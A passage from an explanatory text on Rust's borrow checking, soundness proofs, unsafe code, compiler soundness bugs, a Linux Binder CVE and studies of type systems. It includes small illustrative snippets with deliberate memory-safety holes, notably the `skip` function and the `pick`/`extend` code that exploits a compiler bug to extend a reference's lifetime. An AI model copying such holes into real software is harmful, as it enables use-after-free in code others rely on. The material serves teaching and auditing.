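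3. Follow the loans forwards. Line 2 creates a shared loan of `v`. The loan covers the whole vector because `v[0]` calls a function that borrows the vector and returns a reference to one element. At lines 3 and 4, `first` depends on this loan.
4. Look for conflicts. A write conflicts with any loan of the same data that a live reference depends on, and a read conflicts only with an exclusive one. `push` takes an exclusive borrow of `v`, which counts as a write. At line 3, `first` is live and depends on the loan of `v`, so the checker reports an error.

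If the programmer swaps lines 3 and 4, the program prints the first element and then extends the vector. `first` is no longer live at the `push`, so the checker accepts the program. Rust's original borrow checker would have rejected even this version, because it made a reference last until the end of its block. Huey (2026), in *Enabling the next iteration of the borrow checker on nightly*, dates its replacement to 2019. The current algorithm is called NLL, for "non-lexical lifetimes", because lifetimes no longer have to match blocks in the text.

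A loop over a vector can hold a shared borrow of the vector until the last pass, so the same steps reject such a loop if it adds or removes elements.

Where two paths meet, the checker combines the loans from both, since either path may have run. It analyses a loop repeatedly until a pass adds no new loans. Because a function contains finitely many borrow expressions, the check always terminates, even for a program that runs forever.

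Wu and colleagues also describe a version that needs no backwards step. When line 3 changes `v`, this version marks `first` as invalid, then reports an error only if a later line uses `first`. It gives the same result as the four steps above for both orderings of the program.

At a function call, the checker reads only the called function's signature, the line that declares its parameters and result. The signature must therefore state which arguments the result may depend on. This function, adapted from an example by Wu and colleagues, states it wrongly:

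```rust
fn choose<'a, 'b>(x: &'a mut i32, y: &'b mut i32, d: bool) -> &'b mut i32 {
    if d { x } else { y }
}
```

`'a` and `'b` are lifetimes. According to the signature, the result depends only on `y`, but the function can also return `x`. The checker rejects the function when it examines the body, because otherwise a caller could free the data behind `x` and then read it through the result. The programmer can correct the signature by using the same lifetime for `x`, `y` and the result. Callers must then treat the result as depending on both `x` and `y`, even if they always pass `true` for `d`.

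### Safe programs that Rust rejects

A C++ programmer can ask a vector to reserve space in advance:

```cpp
std::vector<int> v;
v.reserve(10);
v.push_back(10);
int& first = v[0];
v.push_back(20);
std::cout << first;
```

This program is correct and prints 10. The block has room for ten numbers, so the second `push_back` does not need a new one and `first` remains valid. Rust nevertheless rejects the equivalent program:

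```rust
let mut v = Vec::with_capacity(10);
v.push(10);
let first = &v[0];
v.push(20);               // error
println!("{}", first);
```

The four steps give the same result as before. The signature of `push` requires exclusive access to the vector and doesn't include its spare capacity, so the checker treats every `push` as one that could invalidate existing references. A refinement type could state that `push` leaves references valid when the length is below the capacity, but callers would then have to show that this condition holds. Rust programmers usually choose the easier fix of writing `let first = v[0];`, which copies the number instead of borrowing it.

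Chen and colleagues describe a false alarm that is harder to avoid. A program opens a log file, lends it to a reader, and wraps up the eventual call to `close` in a small function that it will run later:

```rust
let f = open("app.log");
let r = &f;
let finish = move || close(f);   // error: f is on loan to r
show(read(r));
finish();
```

The program closes the file only after its last use of `r`, so it is safe. But `finish` takes ownership of `f` on the third line, and Rust forbids moving a value while a reference to it is in use. The type of `f` is still `File`, which does not show the loan, so the compiler could not pass this information on to `finish`. Chen and colleagues propose a type system that could. While `r` is in use, the type of `f` records that its holder may read the file, may not close it yet, and must close it eventually. When the loan ends, the holder automatically regains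 permission to close the file.

### A borrow returned on only one branch

Programmers run into another false alarm more often. This function, a simplified version of one in Huey's announcement, looks up a key in a table and adds an entry if there is none:

```rust
fn get_or_add<'r>(map: &'r mut HashMap<u32, u32>, key: u32) -> &'r mut u32 {
    match map.get_mut(&key) {
        Some(value) => value,
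        None => {
            map.insert(key, 0);
            map.get_mut(&key).unwrap()
        }
    }
}
```

The first call to `get_mut` borrows the table exclusively. If it finds the key, the function returns a reference to the entry. If not, no reference to any entry exists, so the function can safely change the table.

NLL rejects the function. It represents a lifetime as a single set of points in the program. Since the function may return the borrowed reference to its caller, the borrow must last for all of `'r`, which extends beyond the end of the function. NLL applies this requirement to both branches, so the borrow is still active in the `None` branch, where it conflicts with `insert`.

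The next algorithm, Polonius, records which loans each reference may depend on at each point in the program. In the `Some` branch, `value` depends on the loan of the table. In the `None` branch, no live reference depends on that loan, so `insert` does not conflict with it and Polonius accepts the function.

Work on Polonius began in 2018. Huey reports that the original version accepted more safe programs than NLL but was far too slow on some of them. A design from 2023 builds on NLL's code. The Rust Project described this version, now called Polonius Alpha, as "less powerful than we hoped", but it is faster and handles the main case that NLL left unsolved. It still rejects, for example, a program that walks along a linked list and advances its reference on only some passes of the loop.

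In August 2026, the developers switched on Polonius Alpha in nightly Rust, the experimental version that they rebuild every day. They wanted users to find slow cases, confusing messages and unsafe programs that it wrongly accepts. The Rust Project's plan for the year had already listed one soundness problem to fix first. Huey tested the 10,000 most downloaded Rust packages and found few significant slowdowns. Among packages with many borrows outside that group, the worst slowdown was two- to threefold.

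Huey aimed to include Polonius Alpha in stable Rust by the end of 2026. Rust Blog's *Announcing Rust 1.100.0* (12 November 2026) does not list it among the main features, so most programmers were probably still using NLL then. Rust Project's *The Borrow Checker Within* leaves the complete algorithm for later, and Huey has no firm plans to extend Alpha once it is stable.

### What has been proved, and for which parts of Rust

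Programmers describe Rust as memory-safe. Researchers have proved borrow checking sound for simplified versions of Rust, each of which omits different parts of the language, but no proof covers the whole language and its compiler.

Weiss and colleagues defined Oxide, a language close to the Rust that programmers write but with every type spelled out. They extended ordinary typing rules so that checking an expression also changes the list of variables. In simplified form:

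> Γ ⊢ e : T ⇒ Γ′

This means that e has type T given the variables and loans in Γ, and Γ′ lists the variables and loans after e. If e moves `a`, then Γ′ marks `a` as unusable. If e borrows `a`, then Γ′ contains a new loan. The rules check the next expression using Γ′, so they track changes that ordinary types miss. Weiss and colleagues proved progress and preservation for Oxide, so its well-typed programs never get stuck. They also compared its results with the Rust compiler's on part of the compiler's official test suite. Oxide leaves out library code that uses `unsafe`, which allows operations the compiler doesn't check for safety, and Weiss and colleagues only sketched how to add vectors.

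In *Sound Borrow-Checking for Rust via Symbolic Semantics (Long Version)*, Ho, Fromherz and Protzenko (2024) work on Aeneas, a tool for proving that Rust programs meet their specifications. Aeneas runs a program on symbols that stand for arbitrary inputs, so one symbolic run can cover every input. In its model of memory, a reference holds the value it borrowed and returns it when the borrow ends, whereas a real machine leaves the value in place and stores its address. Ho and colleagues proved that the two models agree, so if the symbolic run succeeds, the program is safe on a machine with ordinary addresses, whatever its input.

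Their theorem covers a core subset of Rust, now including loops. The symbolic run is sometimes more precise than the compiler's borrow checker, so it can show that some programs that Rust rejects are safe. Ho and colleagues left for later the part of Aeneas that translates Rust programs into mathematical functions that people can reason about.

Neither proof concerns the algorithms in the Rust compiler itself. Wu and colleagues wrote their own implementation of Polonius and proved it correct in Rocq, a program that checks mathematical proofs. Their theorem states that if the checker accepts a program, no step of any run uses a reference to memory that the program has freed. The proof has three parts:

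1. In an actual run, one can record exactly which data each reference borrows. The checker's loans always cover at least this much, so the checker detects every conflict that could occur.
2. References to the same data form a chain in the order in which the program created them, although shared references can branch off from it. Using an older reference in a conflicting way makes the newer ones invalid.
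3. Only an action through an older part of the chain can free memory that a newer reference points to. By then the newer reference is already invalid, so any attempt to use it is an error that the checker would have reported.

The theorem covers functions, structures and single values on the heap, which is memory that programs allocate as they run. It leaves out closures (functions that capture variables, like `finish`), slices, generic types, traits and unsafe code. It also assumes that other parts of the compiler have already checked types, moves and the use of variables that have no value yet.

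Wu and colleagues ran their checker and the official one on 510 test programs, and the results matched on 499. Their checker rejected four programs that the compiler accepted, mainly because it lacks some refinements, and accepted seven that the compiler rejected, mostly because the compiler has stricter rules for signatures. This is good evidence that their implementation is faithful to Polonius, but the theorem is about their implementation, not the compiler's code.

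An AI model wrote most of the formal proof. Wu and colleagues worked out about 100 pages of proofs on paper, then used OpenAI's coding agent Codex, running GPT-6 Astra, to turn them into roughly 61,000 lines of Rocq in two weeks. As with proof-carrying code, a mistake in a proof does no harm if the proof checker catches it. But Rocq cannot check whether the definitions and the theorem describe what people care about. Wu and colleagues wrote those by hand, and a sceptical reader should focus on them.

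### Move: a smaller language with a simpler checker

Move is a language for programs that handle digital assets on blockchains. It lets a programmer declare a type whose values a program cannot copy or discard, so it cannot duplicate a coin or lose it by accident. In this respect, Move's types are closer to linear types than Rust's are.

Move also has references and a borrow checker. Wu and colleagues explain that Move references cannot point to other references, and programs cannot store them inside larger data structures. With these restrictions, the checker can guarantee memory safety without Rust's analysis of lifetimes. It uses regular expressions, a simple kind of pattern, to describe what each reference can reach. The restrictions make some programs awkward to write. For example, a Move program, unlike a Rust program, cannot keep a table of references to objects elsewhere in memory.

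### What ownership does not exclude

A program written in safe Rust can leak memory, meaning that it never frees data it no longer needs. Rust's `Rc` type lets a value have several owners and frees it when no owners remain. If two such values own each other, each always has at least one owner, so the program never frees either. The standard library's `forget` function also takes ownership of a value and deliberately does not clean it up. Rust's designers chose to allow leaks, which can exhaust a machine's memory but do not cause a program to read freed memory.

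The borrowing rules also allow deadlocks, because they do not require threads to take locks in the same order. If one thread holds lock A and waits for lock B, while another holds B and waits for A, neither can continue.

The compiler leaves many errors for run-time checks to catch. `v[7]` compiles even if `v` has three elements, and the program stops when it reaches that line. To avoid borrow errors, programmers sometimes store an element's position instead of a reference to it, but the position can become out of date. If the program removes the first element of a vector, position 0 refers to a different element, or to none if the vector is now empty. Rust does not read freed memory in either case, but the program may silently use the wrong element.

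Nor do the rules ensure that a program is logically correct. In this code, `balance` is a number in a `Mutex` that several threads share:

```rust
if *balance.lock().unwrap() >= 80 {
    *balance.lock().unwrap() -= 80;
}
```

Each line takes the lock, uses the number and releases the lock. If the balance is 100 and two threads run the code together, both may pass the test before either subtracts anything, and the balance ends up at −60. There is no data race, because only one thread at a time uses the number. To prevent the error, the programmer has to hold the lock from the test until after the subtraction. The borrow checker accepts the code with or without this change.

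## Account for the code the checker does not cover

A Rust program that passes the borrow checker can still read freed memory. A library it uses may contain code that the checker did not fully examine. The language's rules may fail to rule out an unsafe program, the compiler may apply the rules wrongly, or the processor may not behave as the rules assume. Anyone who offers or relies on a guarantee should list what it depends on in the libraries, the language rules, the compiler, and the processor.

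### Casts, TypeScript and foreign functions

An escape hatch is a language feature that lets a programmer switch off a check and take responsibility for the property. The most familiar one is the cast, which makes the checker treat a value as having a type that the programmer names:

```python
from typing import cast

n = cast(int, input("Favourite number? "))
print(n + 1)
```

Mypy accepts this program, but `cast` does nothing when the program runs. The user's reply is still text, so the addition fails. Java checks most casts at run time and stops the program if the object has the wrong type.

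TypeScript, which adds static types to JavaScript, is unsound even without casts. Its designers chose this deliberately, so that the checker would accept common JavaScript code. For example, it accepts this:

```typescript
const numbers: number[] = [1, 2, 3];
const mixed: (number | string)[] = numbers;
mixed.push("four");
numbers[3].toFixed();
```

`mixed` and `numbers` are two names for the same list. TypeScript lets a program use a list of numbers as a list of numbers and strings, which is harmless until the program adds a string. The last line then calls a number operation on that string and fails.

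Foreign functions, which are functions written in another language, leave a larger gap. To call a C function from Rust, a programmer declares its types:

```rust
unsafe extern "C" {
    fn count_words(text: *const c_char) -> i64;
}
```

The Rust compiler cannot check this declaration against the C code, just as mypy cannot detect a wrong stub file. Even if the declaration is right, the C function can overwrite any memory that the Rust program uses.

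### Unsafe Rust

Rust allows its most dangerous operations only in code marked with the keyword `unsafe`. Code in an unsafe block can follow raw pointers, which are addresses the borrow checker does not track, and call functions whose requirements the compiler cannot check. The compiler still applies its ordinary checks on types and references there.

A mistake in such a block can cause undefined behaviour, in which case the language guarantees nothing about what the program does. The compiler optimises the program as if undefined behaviour never occurs.

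*Targeted Fuzzing for Unsafe Rust Code* (2025) cites two earlier studies of crates (Rust packages). It reports that 21.3 per cent of crates contain at least one explicit unsafe statement, and that the share is about half when dependencies are included. Current figures may differ. Most programs also use unsafe code in the standard library. `Vec`, for example, is a few thousand lines of code with unsafe parts, but programmers can call its public functions from safe code.

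### The contract that an unsafe library must meet

Such a library must ensure that no safe program can cause undefined behaviour through it, however strangely the program uses its public functions. Here is a small stack of numbers with room for eight:

```rust
pub struct Stack { items: [i32; 8], len: usize }

impl Stack {
    pub fn new() -> Stack { Stack { items: [0; 8], len: 0 } }

    pub fn push(&mut self, x: i32) -> bool {
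        if self.len == 8 { return false; }
        self.items[self.len] = x;
        self.len += 1;
        true
    }

    pub fn top(&self) -> Option<i32> {
        if self.len == 0 { return None; }
        // SAFETY: len is at most 8
        Some(unsafe { *self.items.get_unchecked(self.len - 1) })
    }
}
```

`get_unchecked` reads an array without testing the position. This is safe here because `len` starts at 0 and `push` never raises it above 8. Now suppose a colleague adds a function for leaving a slot empty:

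```rust
    pub fn skip(&mut self) { self.len += 1; }
```

The new function has no unsafe code, and the compiler accepts it. But after nine calls to `skip`, `top` reads past the end of the array. A reviewer who read only the unsafe blocks would miss this mistake, so the reviewer has to read all the code that can change `len`. That code is all in one module because `len` is private.

RustBelt, which Ralf Jung and colleagues published in 2018, states the contract mathematically. Typing rules alone are not enough for this. *Modular Formal Verification of Rust Programs with Unsafe Blocks* (2022) explains that unsafe code does not satisfy Rust's safe typing rules, and that rules loose enough to accept it would be unsound. RustBelt therefore defines each type by how its values behave, as Timany and colleagues recommend. A function of type S → T, for instance, must run without undefined behaviour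 when it receives any value that behaves like an S, and anything it returns must behave like a T. The argument has three parts:

1. Safe code that satisfies the typing rules behaves as its types require.
2. A complete program that behaves as its types require never causes undefined behaviour.
3. For each library with unsafe code inside, somebody must prove separately that its public functions behave as their types require.

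For `Stack`, the definition of the type would include the condition that `len` is at most 8. `push` keeps this condition true but `skip` does not, so the third part of the proof would fail at `skip`.

Safe code that uses libraries with unsafe internals is guaranteed to be free of undefined behaviour only if somebody has proved those libraries correct. Jung and colleagues did this for several standard types, including `Mutex`, but most libraries have no such proof. *Refactoring and Equivalence in Rust* (2026) leaves out this condition when it summarises RustBelt's result. Like Oxide, RustBelt covers only a simplified language.

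Many libraries break the contract. *UnsafeChecker* (2026) describes a tool that scanned more than 100,000 crates. A manual check of a sample of about 10,000 found 114 bugs in 83 crates, and a second tool, Miri, confirmed all of the bugs. Some were errors such as integer overflow, which do not corrupt memory by themselves. In *Agentic Discovery of Soundness Bugs in Safe Rust Bindings* (2026), AI agents audited 16 crates and the Linux kernel's Rust interfaces. They found 225 instances of undefined behaviour, and test programs with no unsafe code of their own could trigger 202 of them. The audits covered too few crates to show how common such errors are.

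### Which aliases unsafe code may create

Authors of unsafe code also need to know which aliases they may create, because the compiler uses the borrowing rules to optimise programs. Villani, Hostert and colleagues (2025), in *Tree Borrows*, give this example:

```rust
fn write_both(x: &mut i32, y: &mut i32) -> i32 {
    *x = 13;
    *y = 20;
    *x
}
```

In safe Rust, two exclusive references cannot refer to the same number, so the function always returns 13. The compiler could therefore skip the final read and return 13 directly. But unsafe code can turn one raw pointer into two exclusive references and pass both to the function, which then returns 20 without the optimisation and 13 with it. To justify the optimisation, Rust's rules have to make the caller's code undefined behaviour without ruling out reasonable unsafe code.

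Tree Borrows is a proposed definition. It arranges references in a tree, in which each reference is a child of the reference or variable that the program made it from. Each has a state, which can change whenever the program reads or writes the data. Consider this program:

```rust
let mut n = 42;
let p = &mut n as *mut i32;
let x = unsafe { &mut *p };
let y = unsafe { &mut *p };
*x = 13;
*y = 20;
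```

1. The program makes both `x` and `y` from `p`, so they are siblings. Both start as "Reserved", which means that neither has written anything yet.
2. The write through `x` makes `x` "Unique". Since `y` is neither `x` nor a descendant of `x`, the same write makes `y` "Disabled".
3. The write through `y` uses a disabled reference, which is undefined behaviour.

An earlier model, Stacked Borrows, kept references in a stack and forbade some common habits, such as taking the address of an array's first element and using it to reach the others, as C programmers often do. Villani and colleagues ran the tests of the 30,000 most downloaded crates under both Stacked Borrows and their own model, Tree Borrows, which rejected 54 per cent fewer tests. They also proved that Tree Borrows justifies many optimisations, including reordering neighbouring reads, which Stacked Borrows does not allow. In 2025,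 it was still a conjecture that every program the borrow checker accepts also obeys Tree Borrows.

Rust has not adopted either model as its official definition. *Towards verifying unsafe Rust programs against Rust's pointer-aliasing restrictions* (2026) notes that the official rules are neither formally defined nor final. It adds that several tools for proving unsafe Rust correct, including Verus and RefinedRust, ignore the aliasing rules and are therefore unsound. A program that one of these tools proves correct might still break when the compiler optimises it.

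### Testing with Miri

Miri is an interpreter that runs a Rust program step by step and reports undefined behaviour when it occurs. It can apply either aliasing model. In *Miri* (2026), Jung, Kimock and colleagues tried it on more than 100,000 libraries, and it could run over 70 per cent of their tests. It has found dozens of real bugs, and the standard library's developers now run it routinely.

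Miri is a dynamic check, so it covers only the runs that somebody tries. If a program's threads can interleave in several ways, Miri tests one interleaving unless the user asks for more. *What's "new" in Miri (and also, there's a Miri paper!)* (2025) also warns that code that passes today may count as undefined behaviour in future. *A Mixed-Methods Study on the Implications of Unsafe Rust* (2024) reports that Miri does not fully support programs that call other languages, and such calls are one of the main reasons for writing unsafe code.

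### A hole in the rules of Java and Scala

A program with no escape hatches is still at risk if the language's own rules are unsound. In 2016, Nada Amin and Ross Tate showed that this was true of both Java and Scala. Their Java example works roughly like this:

```java
class Between<A, B extends A> {}

class Use<A> {
    <B extends A> A upcast(Between<A, B> evidence, B value) { return value; }
}

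<T, U> U convert(T value) {
    Between<U, ? super T> evidence = null;
    return new Use<U>().upcast(evidence, value);
}
```

An object of type `Between<U, ? super T>` can exist only if some type is both a supertype of T and a subtype of U. If there is such a type, T is a subtype of U, and the program may treat any T as a U. No such type exists for whole numbers and text, so no such object can exist. But Java lets a variable of any class type hold `null`, the value for "no object". `convert` supplies `null` in place of the object that would show T is a subtype of U, and the checker then accepts a number as text.

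At run time, the Java virtual machine's own type check stops the program with an error, so the hole does not corrupt memory. A dynamic check can therefore be worth keeping even if it looks redundant.

*Rust's Type Checker Implementation Is Unsound* notes that Amin and Tate traced the problem to an interaction between language features. A correct soundness proof for a simplified Java without `null` could still miss it. So a soundness proof that leaves out a feature doesn't cover programs that use that feature, even if the feature looks harmless.

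### Thirty soundness issues in the Rust compiler

A compiler may also fail to implement its language's rules. Sim, Ryu and Hong (2026), in *Rust's Type Checker Implementation Is Unsound*, examined reports of the Rust compiler accepting programs that it should reject. They selected the reports in five steps:

1. They collected the 969 issues that users and developers had filed between January 2022 and September 2025 with labels related to type checking.
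2. They kept those labelled as bugs or as unsound, and removed those about documentation, error messages, crashes and experimental features. This left 320.
3. They read each one and kept the 27 that included code which the reporter thought the compiler should reject, and in which the compiler was at fault.
4. They removed four duplicates, leaving 23.
5. They added seven that an earlier study had found and their labels had missed, for a total of 30.

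An issue counted as fixed if version 1.93.0 of the compiler rejected the code. In one case it only gave a warning.

| Consequence | Issues | Fixed | Confirmed but not fixed | Reported only |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Possible memory error | 11 | 7 | 3 | 1 |
| A harmless library update can stop other programs compiling | 1 | 1 | 0 | 0 |
| The compiler accepts one program but rejects similar ones | 17 | 10 | 1 | 6 |
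| Misleading behaviour | 1 | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| Total | 30 | 18 | 4 | 8 |

If the property is memory safety, only the 11 issues in the first row are missed violations. One inconsistency is that the compiler accepts a function that returns an empty array but rejects the same function with a one-element array. An empty array holds no references, so returning it cannot violate memory safety.

One of the memory errors needs only a few lines. With different names, it looks like this:

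```rust
fn pick<'a>(v: &'a i32, w: &'static &'a i32) -> &'static i32 { v }

fn extend<'a>(v: &'a i32) -> &'static i32 {
    let f: fn(&'a i32, _) -> &'static i32 = pick;
    f(v, &&0)
}
```

The lifetime `'static` lasts for the program's whole run. The type of `w` makes sense only if `'a` lasts that long too, so the compiler assumes this when it checks `pick`. It should then check the assumption wherever a program uses `pick`, but it doesn't when the program stores `pick` in the variable `f`. `extend` can therefore turn any reference into a `'static` one. A program with no unsafe code could then free the data and still read it through that reference. The bug was first reported in 2015 and is still present in version 1.93.0.

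Such bugs went undiscovered for an average of 1,291 days, or about three and a half years, after the release that introduced them. The longest gap was 3,552 days. The 18 fixed bugs took a further 324 days on average to fix, but this figure excludes those still open.

Sim and colleagues attribute the delay to the unusual combinations of features that most of these bugs require. Half of the issues involve associated types, which belong to a trait (a set of functions that a type must provide). The compiler also gives no sign that anything is wrong. An attacker can deliberately write code that triggers such a bug, so anyone who runs strangers' Rust code needs a sandbox as well as the compiler's checks.

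Sim and colleagues found that three formal models of Rust could not express any of the 30 issues. RustBelt and a newer model, Borrow Calculus, include lifetimes but not traits or the kind of unstated assumption in `pick`. A model by Jonatan Milewski covers traits but not lifetimes, and its rules against conflicting definitions leave out associated types. The proofs remain correct for the languages they describe, but many of the bugs involve interactions between lifetimes and traits.

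Testing the compiler automatically is also hard, because a tester needs an independent way to decide which programs the compiler should reject. Miri and AddressSanitizer detected all 11 memory errors when Sim and colleagues ran the offending programs, but neither tool can detect the errors in the other 19 programs. The a-mir-formality project is building an executable model of Rust's type system that might eventually detect them. So far the model can express only five of the 30 programs, and it correctly rejected three of those. The official documentation is not a sufficient guide either, because it leaves some of the relevant rules vague.

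The figure of 30 is probably too low, because the selection depended on labels and excluded experimental features. It also can't be converted into a rate, because nobody knows how many Rust programs contain one of these combinations.

### Auditing the trusted base

The hardware can also undermine a guarantee, because processors use speculative execution, running instructions before it is certain that the program needs them, and attackers can sometimes use its side effects to read protected data. For a Rust program, an auditor can start with a list like this:

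| Layer | What to record | Where to look |
|---|---|---|
| Escape hatches | Unsafe blocks, foreign functions and the code they rely on | The program and every library it uses |
| Rules | Features that the soundness proofs leave out | The definition of the language in each proof |
| Checker | The compiler's version and its open soundness bugs | The compiler's issue tracker, under the label `I-unsound` |
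| Hardware | Known processor flaws and the protections against them | Notices from the manufacturer and the operating system's developers |

Unsafe code usually needs the most reading, but the amount of it is a poor guide to the risk. *Crustify* (2026) compares two Rust libraries that wrap the same C code. One limits each of its 2,097 unsafe blocks to a single operation, so they contain 17 per cent fewer lines in total than the other library's 1,004 blocks. In the second library, 400 blocks mix several unsafe operations, which makes them harder to review.

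Developers can make an audit easier by keeping unsafe code in a few places. *Tock* (2026) covers ten years of an operating system for small devices, whose developers forbid unsafe code in some of its crates. The kernel grew considerably over that time, while the amount of unsafe code stayed steady. But in the crates that allowed unsafe code, contributors kept using it in new ways, and the developers wished they had provided more safe wrappers.

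The first vulnerability recorded in the Linux kernel's Rust code shows how an auditor can narrow the search. The entry, MITRE's *CVE-2025-68260* (2025), dates from 16 December 2025. It concerns the Rust version of Binder, which Android's processes use to communicate. An auditor could find the bug in four steps:

1. Find the unsafe operation, which here is `unsafe { node_inner.death_list.remove(self) }`. It removes an item from a linked list, in which each item holds the addresses of its neighbours.
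2. Write down what it requires. No other thread may change the item's links at the same time. The programmers' comment justifies this by stating that an item is always either in this list, to which the thread has exclusive access, or in no list.
3. Find all the code that could make the comment false, which means any code that moves items between lists.
4. Check that code, including what other threads can do while it runs. A function called `Node::release` takes a lock, moves all the items to a temporary list, releases the lock and then goes through the temporary list. Meanwhile another thread can call `remove` on one of those items, and both threads change the same links.

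The fix changed `Node::release` to take items directly from the original list. As with `skip`, the unsafe operation depended on code outside its own block. The programmers could also have avoided the requirement by writing a `remove` that checks which list an item is in, though this would have been somewhat slower. One reply under the announcement by kernel developer Greg Kroah-Hartman (gregkh, 2025) calls the requirement "leaky" because it involves other lists.

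Kroah-Hartman wrote that the bug could only cause a crash. He added that the kernel's developers had recorded 159 vulnerabilities in its C code on the same day. However, the kernel has far more C than Rust, so the two counts are not a fair comparison of the languages.

Red Hat's *CVE-2026-23194* describes a later bug in the same driver, which tried to write eight bytes past the end of a buffer. A run-time check caught the attempt and returned an error. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-43434* describes another later bug, which let the driver use a region of memory after another region had replaced it at the same address. A local attacker could then write to pages that should be read-only and, using a second vulnerability, might gain further privileges.

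## Measure what the check achieves

A fairer comparison than the Linux kernel's raw vulnerability counts requires deciding which effects of a check to measure. A check may eliminate the errors it targets but barely change the total number of defects. It also takes up programmers' time, though it may save some later. Most studies measure only the targeted errors, only the total defects, or only the programmers' time.

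### Experiments with programmers

The most direct way to measure how much time a type checker adds is to give programmers the same tasks with and without one. For an experiment in 2010, Stefan Hanenberg built a language called Purity in two versions, one with static type checks and one with dynamic ones. Forty-nine people spent an average of 27 hours each writing a scanner, which splits a text into words and symbols, and a parser, which works out how they fit together. According to *An experiment about static and dynamic type systems* (2011) on Wadler's Blog, the 25 who used the dynamic version finished the scanner in an average of 5.2 hours, significantly faster than the 24 who used the static version. The two groups' parsers did not differ significantly in quality. It Will Never Work in Theory's *An Experiment About Static and Dynamic Type Systems* (2012) repeats Hanenberg's warning against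 drawing general conclusions from one experiment. Each person wrote a small program alone and from scratch, so types had little chance to help as documentation for other people's code.

In *An empirical study on the impact of static typing on software maintainability*, Hanenberg, Kleinschmager and colleagues (2013) studied work on existing code. Their subjects used both Java and Groovy, a dynamic language that can be written like Java without type annotations, and the researchers measured the time until a program passed all its tests. Static types significantly reduced the time needed to use undocumented classes and to fix type errors. They made no significant difference to the time needed to fix semantic errors, such as calling an object's operations in the wrong order, as when a program reads a file it has already closed. Java's types don't track the order of calls, so this result is not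 evidence against typestate or ownership, which can track it.

The main reason to doubt the positive results is that the subjects had no documentation and only a simple editor. Petersen, Hanenberg and Robbes (2014) warn that modern code completion and navigation tools could change such results drastically.

The picture from other experiments that Hanenberg and colleagues review is similarly mixed:

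| Year | Comparison | Subjects | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1998 | C with and without checks on function arguments | 34 | Checks saved time on one task, with no significant difference on the other |
| 2009 | Ruby with an added type checker (observation only) | 4 | Only 13.4 per cent of the checker's messages were informative |
| 2011 | Java with casts, and Groovy without them | 27 | Casts slowed trivial tasks, with no significant difference on longer ones |
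| 2012 | Java and Groovy, fixing errors | 31 | Java was faster for type errors but not for semantic errors |
| 2012 | Java and Groovy, using an undocumented library | 27 | Static types were faster on three tasks, dynamic types on two |

In the last experiment, static types seemed to help most when a task involved many types or complicated ones. On simpler tasks, people using static types worked more systematically and so more slowly.

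The differences between programmers can be much larger than the effect of the check. The Shape of Code (2014) puts the delay from leaving out argument checks in the 1998 experiment at around 10 per cent, about a fifth of the variation between subjects. Task order had a larger effect, around 30 per cent. An experiment with a few dozen people can easily miss a 10 per cent effect, so a null result is weak evidence that types make no difference.

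### Bugs in public repositories

Experiments like these don't cover what happens once a program is in use. Public repositories contain years of changes to real programs, including fixes for bugs that reached other people.

Gao, Bird and Barr (2017), in *To Type or Not to Type*, asked how many such bugs in JavaScript a type checker would have caught. They sampled 400 fixed bugs from 398 projects and proceeded as follows:

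1. Retrieve the code as it was just before the fix.
2. Read the bug report and the fix to learn what the programmer had intended.
3. Add type annotations to the part of the code that the fix changed, spending at most ten minutes per bug for each checker.
4. Run Flow and TypeScript, two type checkers for JavaScript, and record whether they report an error.

In one example, a program passes the number 3 and the text `"0"` to a function that should add two numbers. JavaScript joins them as text, and the program prints 30. If both parameters are annotated as numbers, either checker reports the call as an error.

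Each checker detected 15 per cent of the bugs, or about 60 of the 400. With a sample of that size, the margin of error is about 3.5 percentage points either way. The checkers could not detect most of the other bugs, such as wrong conditions, malformed database queries and failures to implement the specification.

Gao and colleagues think 15 per cent is an underestimate, because it leaves out errors that a checker would have caught while the programmer was still writing the code. But they knew where each bug was, which biases the figure upwards. The figure assumes that developers annotate their code thoroughly and fix every type error.

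In a 2014 study, Baishakhi Ray and colleagues looked for an effect of programming language on defects of all kinds. They collected 1.5 million commits (recorded changes) from 729 projects in 17 languages, and counted a commit as a bug fix if its message contained a word such as "fix" or "error". They then used regression to compare the number of bug fixes in each language, adjusting for each project's age, size, and numbers of commits and developers. Eleven languages had significantly more or fewer bug fixes than average.

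Berger, Hollenbeck and colleagues (2019), in *On the Impact of Programming Languages on Code Quality*, obtained the data and tried to repeat the work. They found several problems:

- Ten professional developers helped to check a sample of 400 commits. Of those that Ray and colleagues had counted as bug fixes, 36 per cent were not, including one that mentioned "infix operators".
- Only 16 of the 41 TypeScript projects contained any TypeScript. Many of the other files were translations of text into human languages, which can have the same `.ts` ending.
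- The data left out most kinds of C++ file. For Google's V8 engine, which is mostly C++, it mainly contained JavaScript tests.
- Testing 16 languages at the usual 5 per cent threshold gives a 56 per cent chance of at least one false finding, if the tests are independent and no language has an effect.

After they corrected for these problems as far as they could, four languages still differed significantly from the average. C++ had an estimated 17 per cent or so more bug fixes, Clojure had about 14 per cent fewer, and Haskell and Ruby were also below average. Clojure and Ruby are dynamically typed, so even at face value the results don't clearly favour static types. They also don't show that the languages caused the differences. For example, bug rates tend to fall as a project ages, and some languages have mostly old projects.

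Three of the original researchers, Ray, Devanbu and Filkov, replied in *Rebuttal to Berger et al., TOPLAS 2019* (2019) that they had reported only a weak association and had warned that it might reflect the kind of people who choose each language. They had given that warning, but Berger and colleagues found that 26 of the 30 citations that discussed the results described them as effects of the language. The exchange continued in *FSE/CACM Rebuttal²* (2019).

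### Why nearly eliminating one class may change little

Even perfect data might show only a small effect on total defects. Ray and colleagues classified about 5 per cent of the bugs as memory errors and 2 per cent as concurrency errors. Berger and colleagues could not reproduce these categories, so the figures are only illustrative.

Suppose a program has 1,000 defects in this mix, including 50 memory errors, and a check removes 98 per cent of the memory errors. It removes 0.98 × 50 = 49 defects and leaves 951. If it also removed all 20 concurrency errors, 931 would remain. When a check targets one class of defect, the fraction of all defects it removes is that class's share of the total multiplied by the fraction of the class it removes. A fall of 5 per cent would be hard to detect in data where a third of the labels are wrong.

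The same check can have a much larger effect on security vulnerabilities. According to The Tech Tribune's *Android Moves to Rust; Cuts Memory Vulnerabilities by 68%*, memory errors made up 76 per cent of vulnerabilities in Android, Google's operating system for phones, before Google changed its approach in 2019.

| | 1,000 defects of all kinds | 1,000 vulnerabilities in Android |
|---|---|---|
| Memory errors at the start | 50 | 760 |
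| Removed by the check | 49 | 745 |
| Left, of all classes | 951 | 255 |

One could truthfully say that this check removes 98 per cent of memory errors, three quarters of a system's vulnerabilities or one twentieth of a program's bugs, depending on which problems are counted.

### Memory errors in Android

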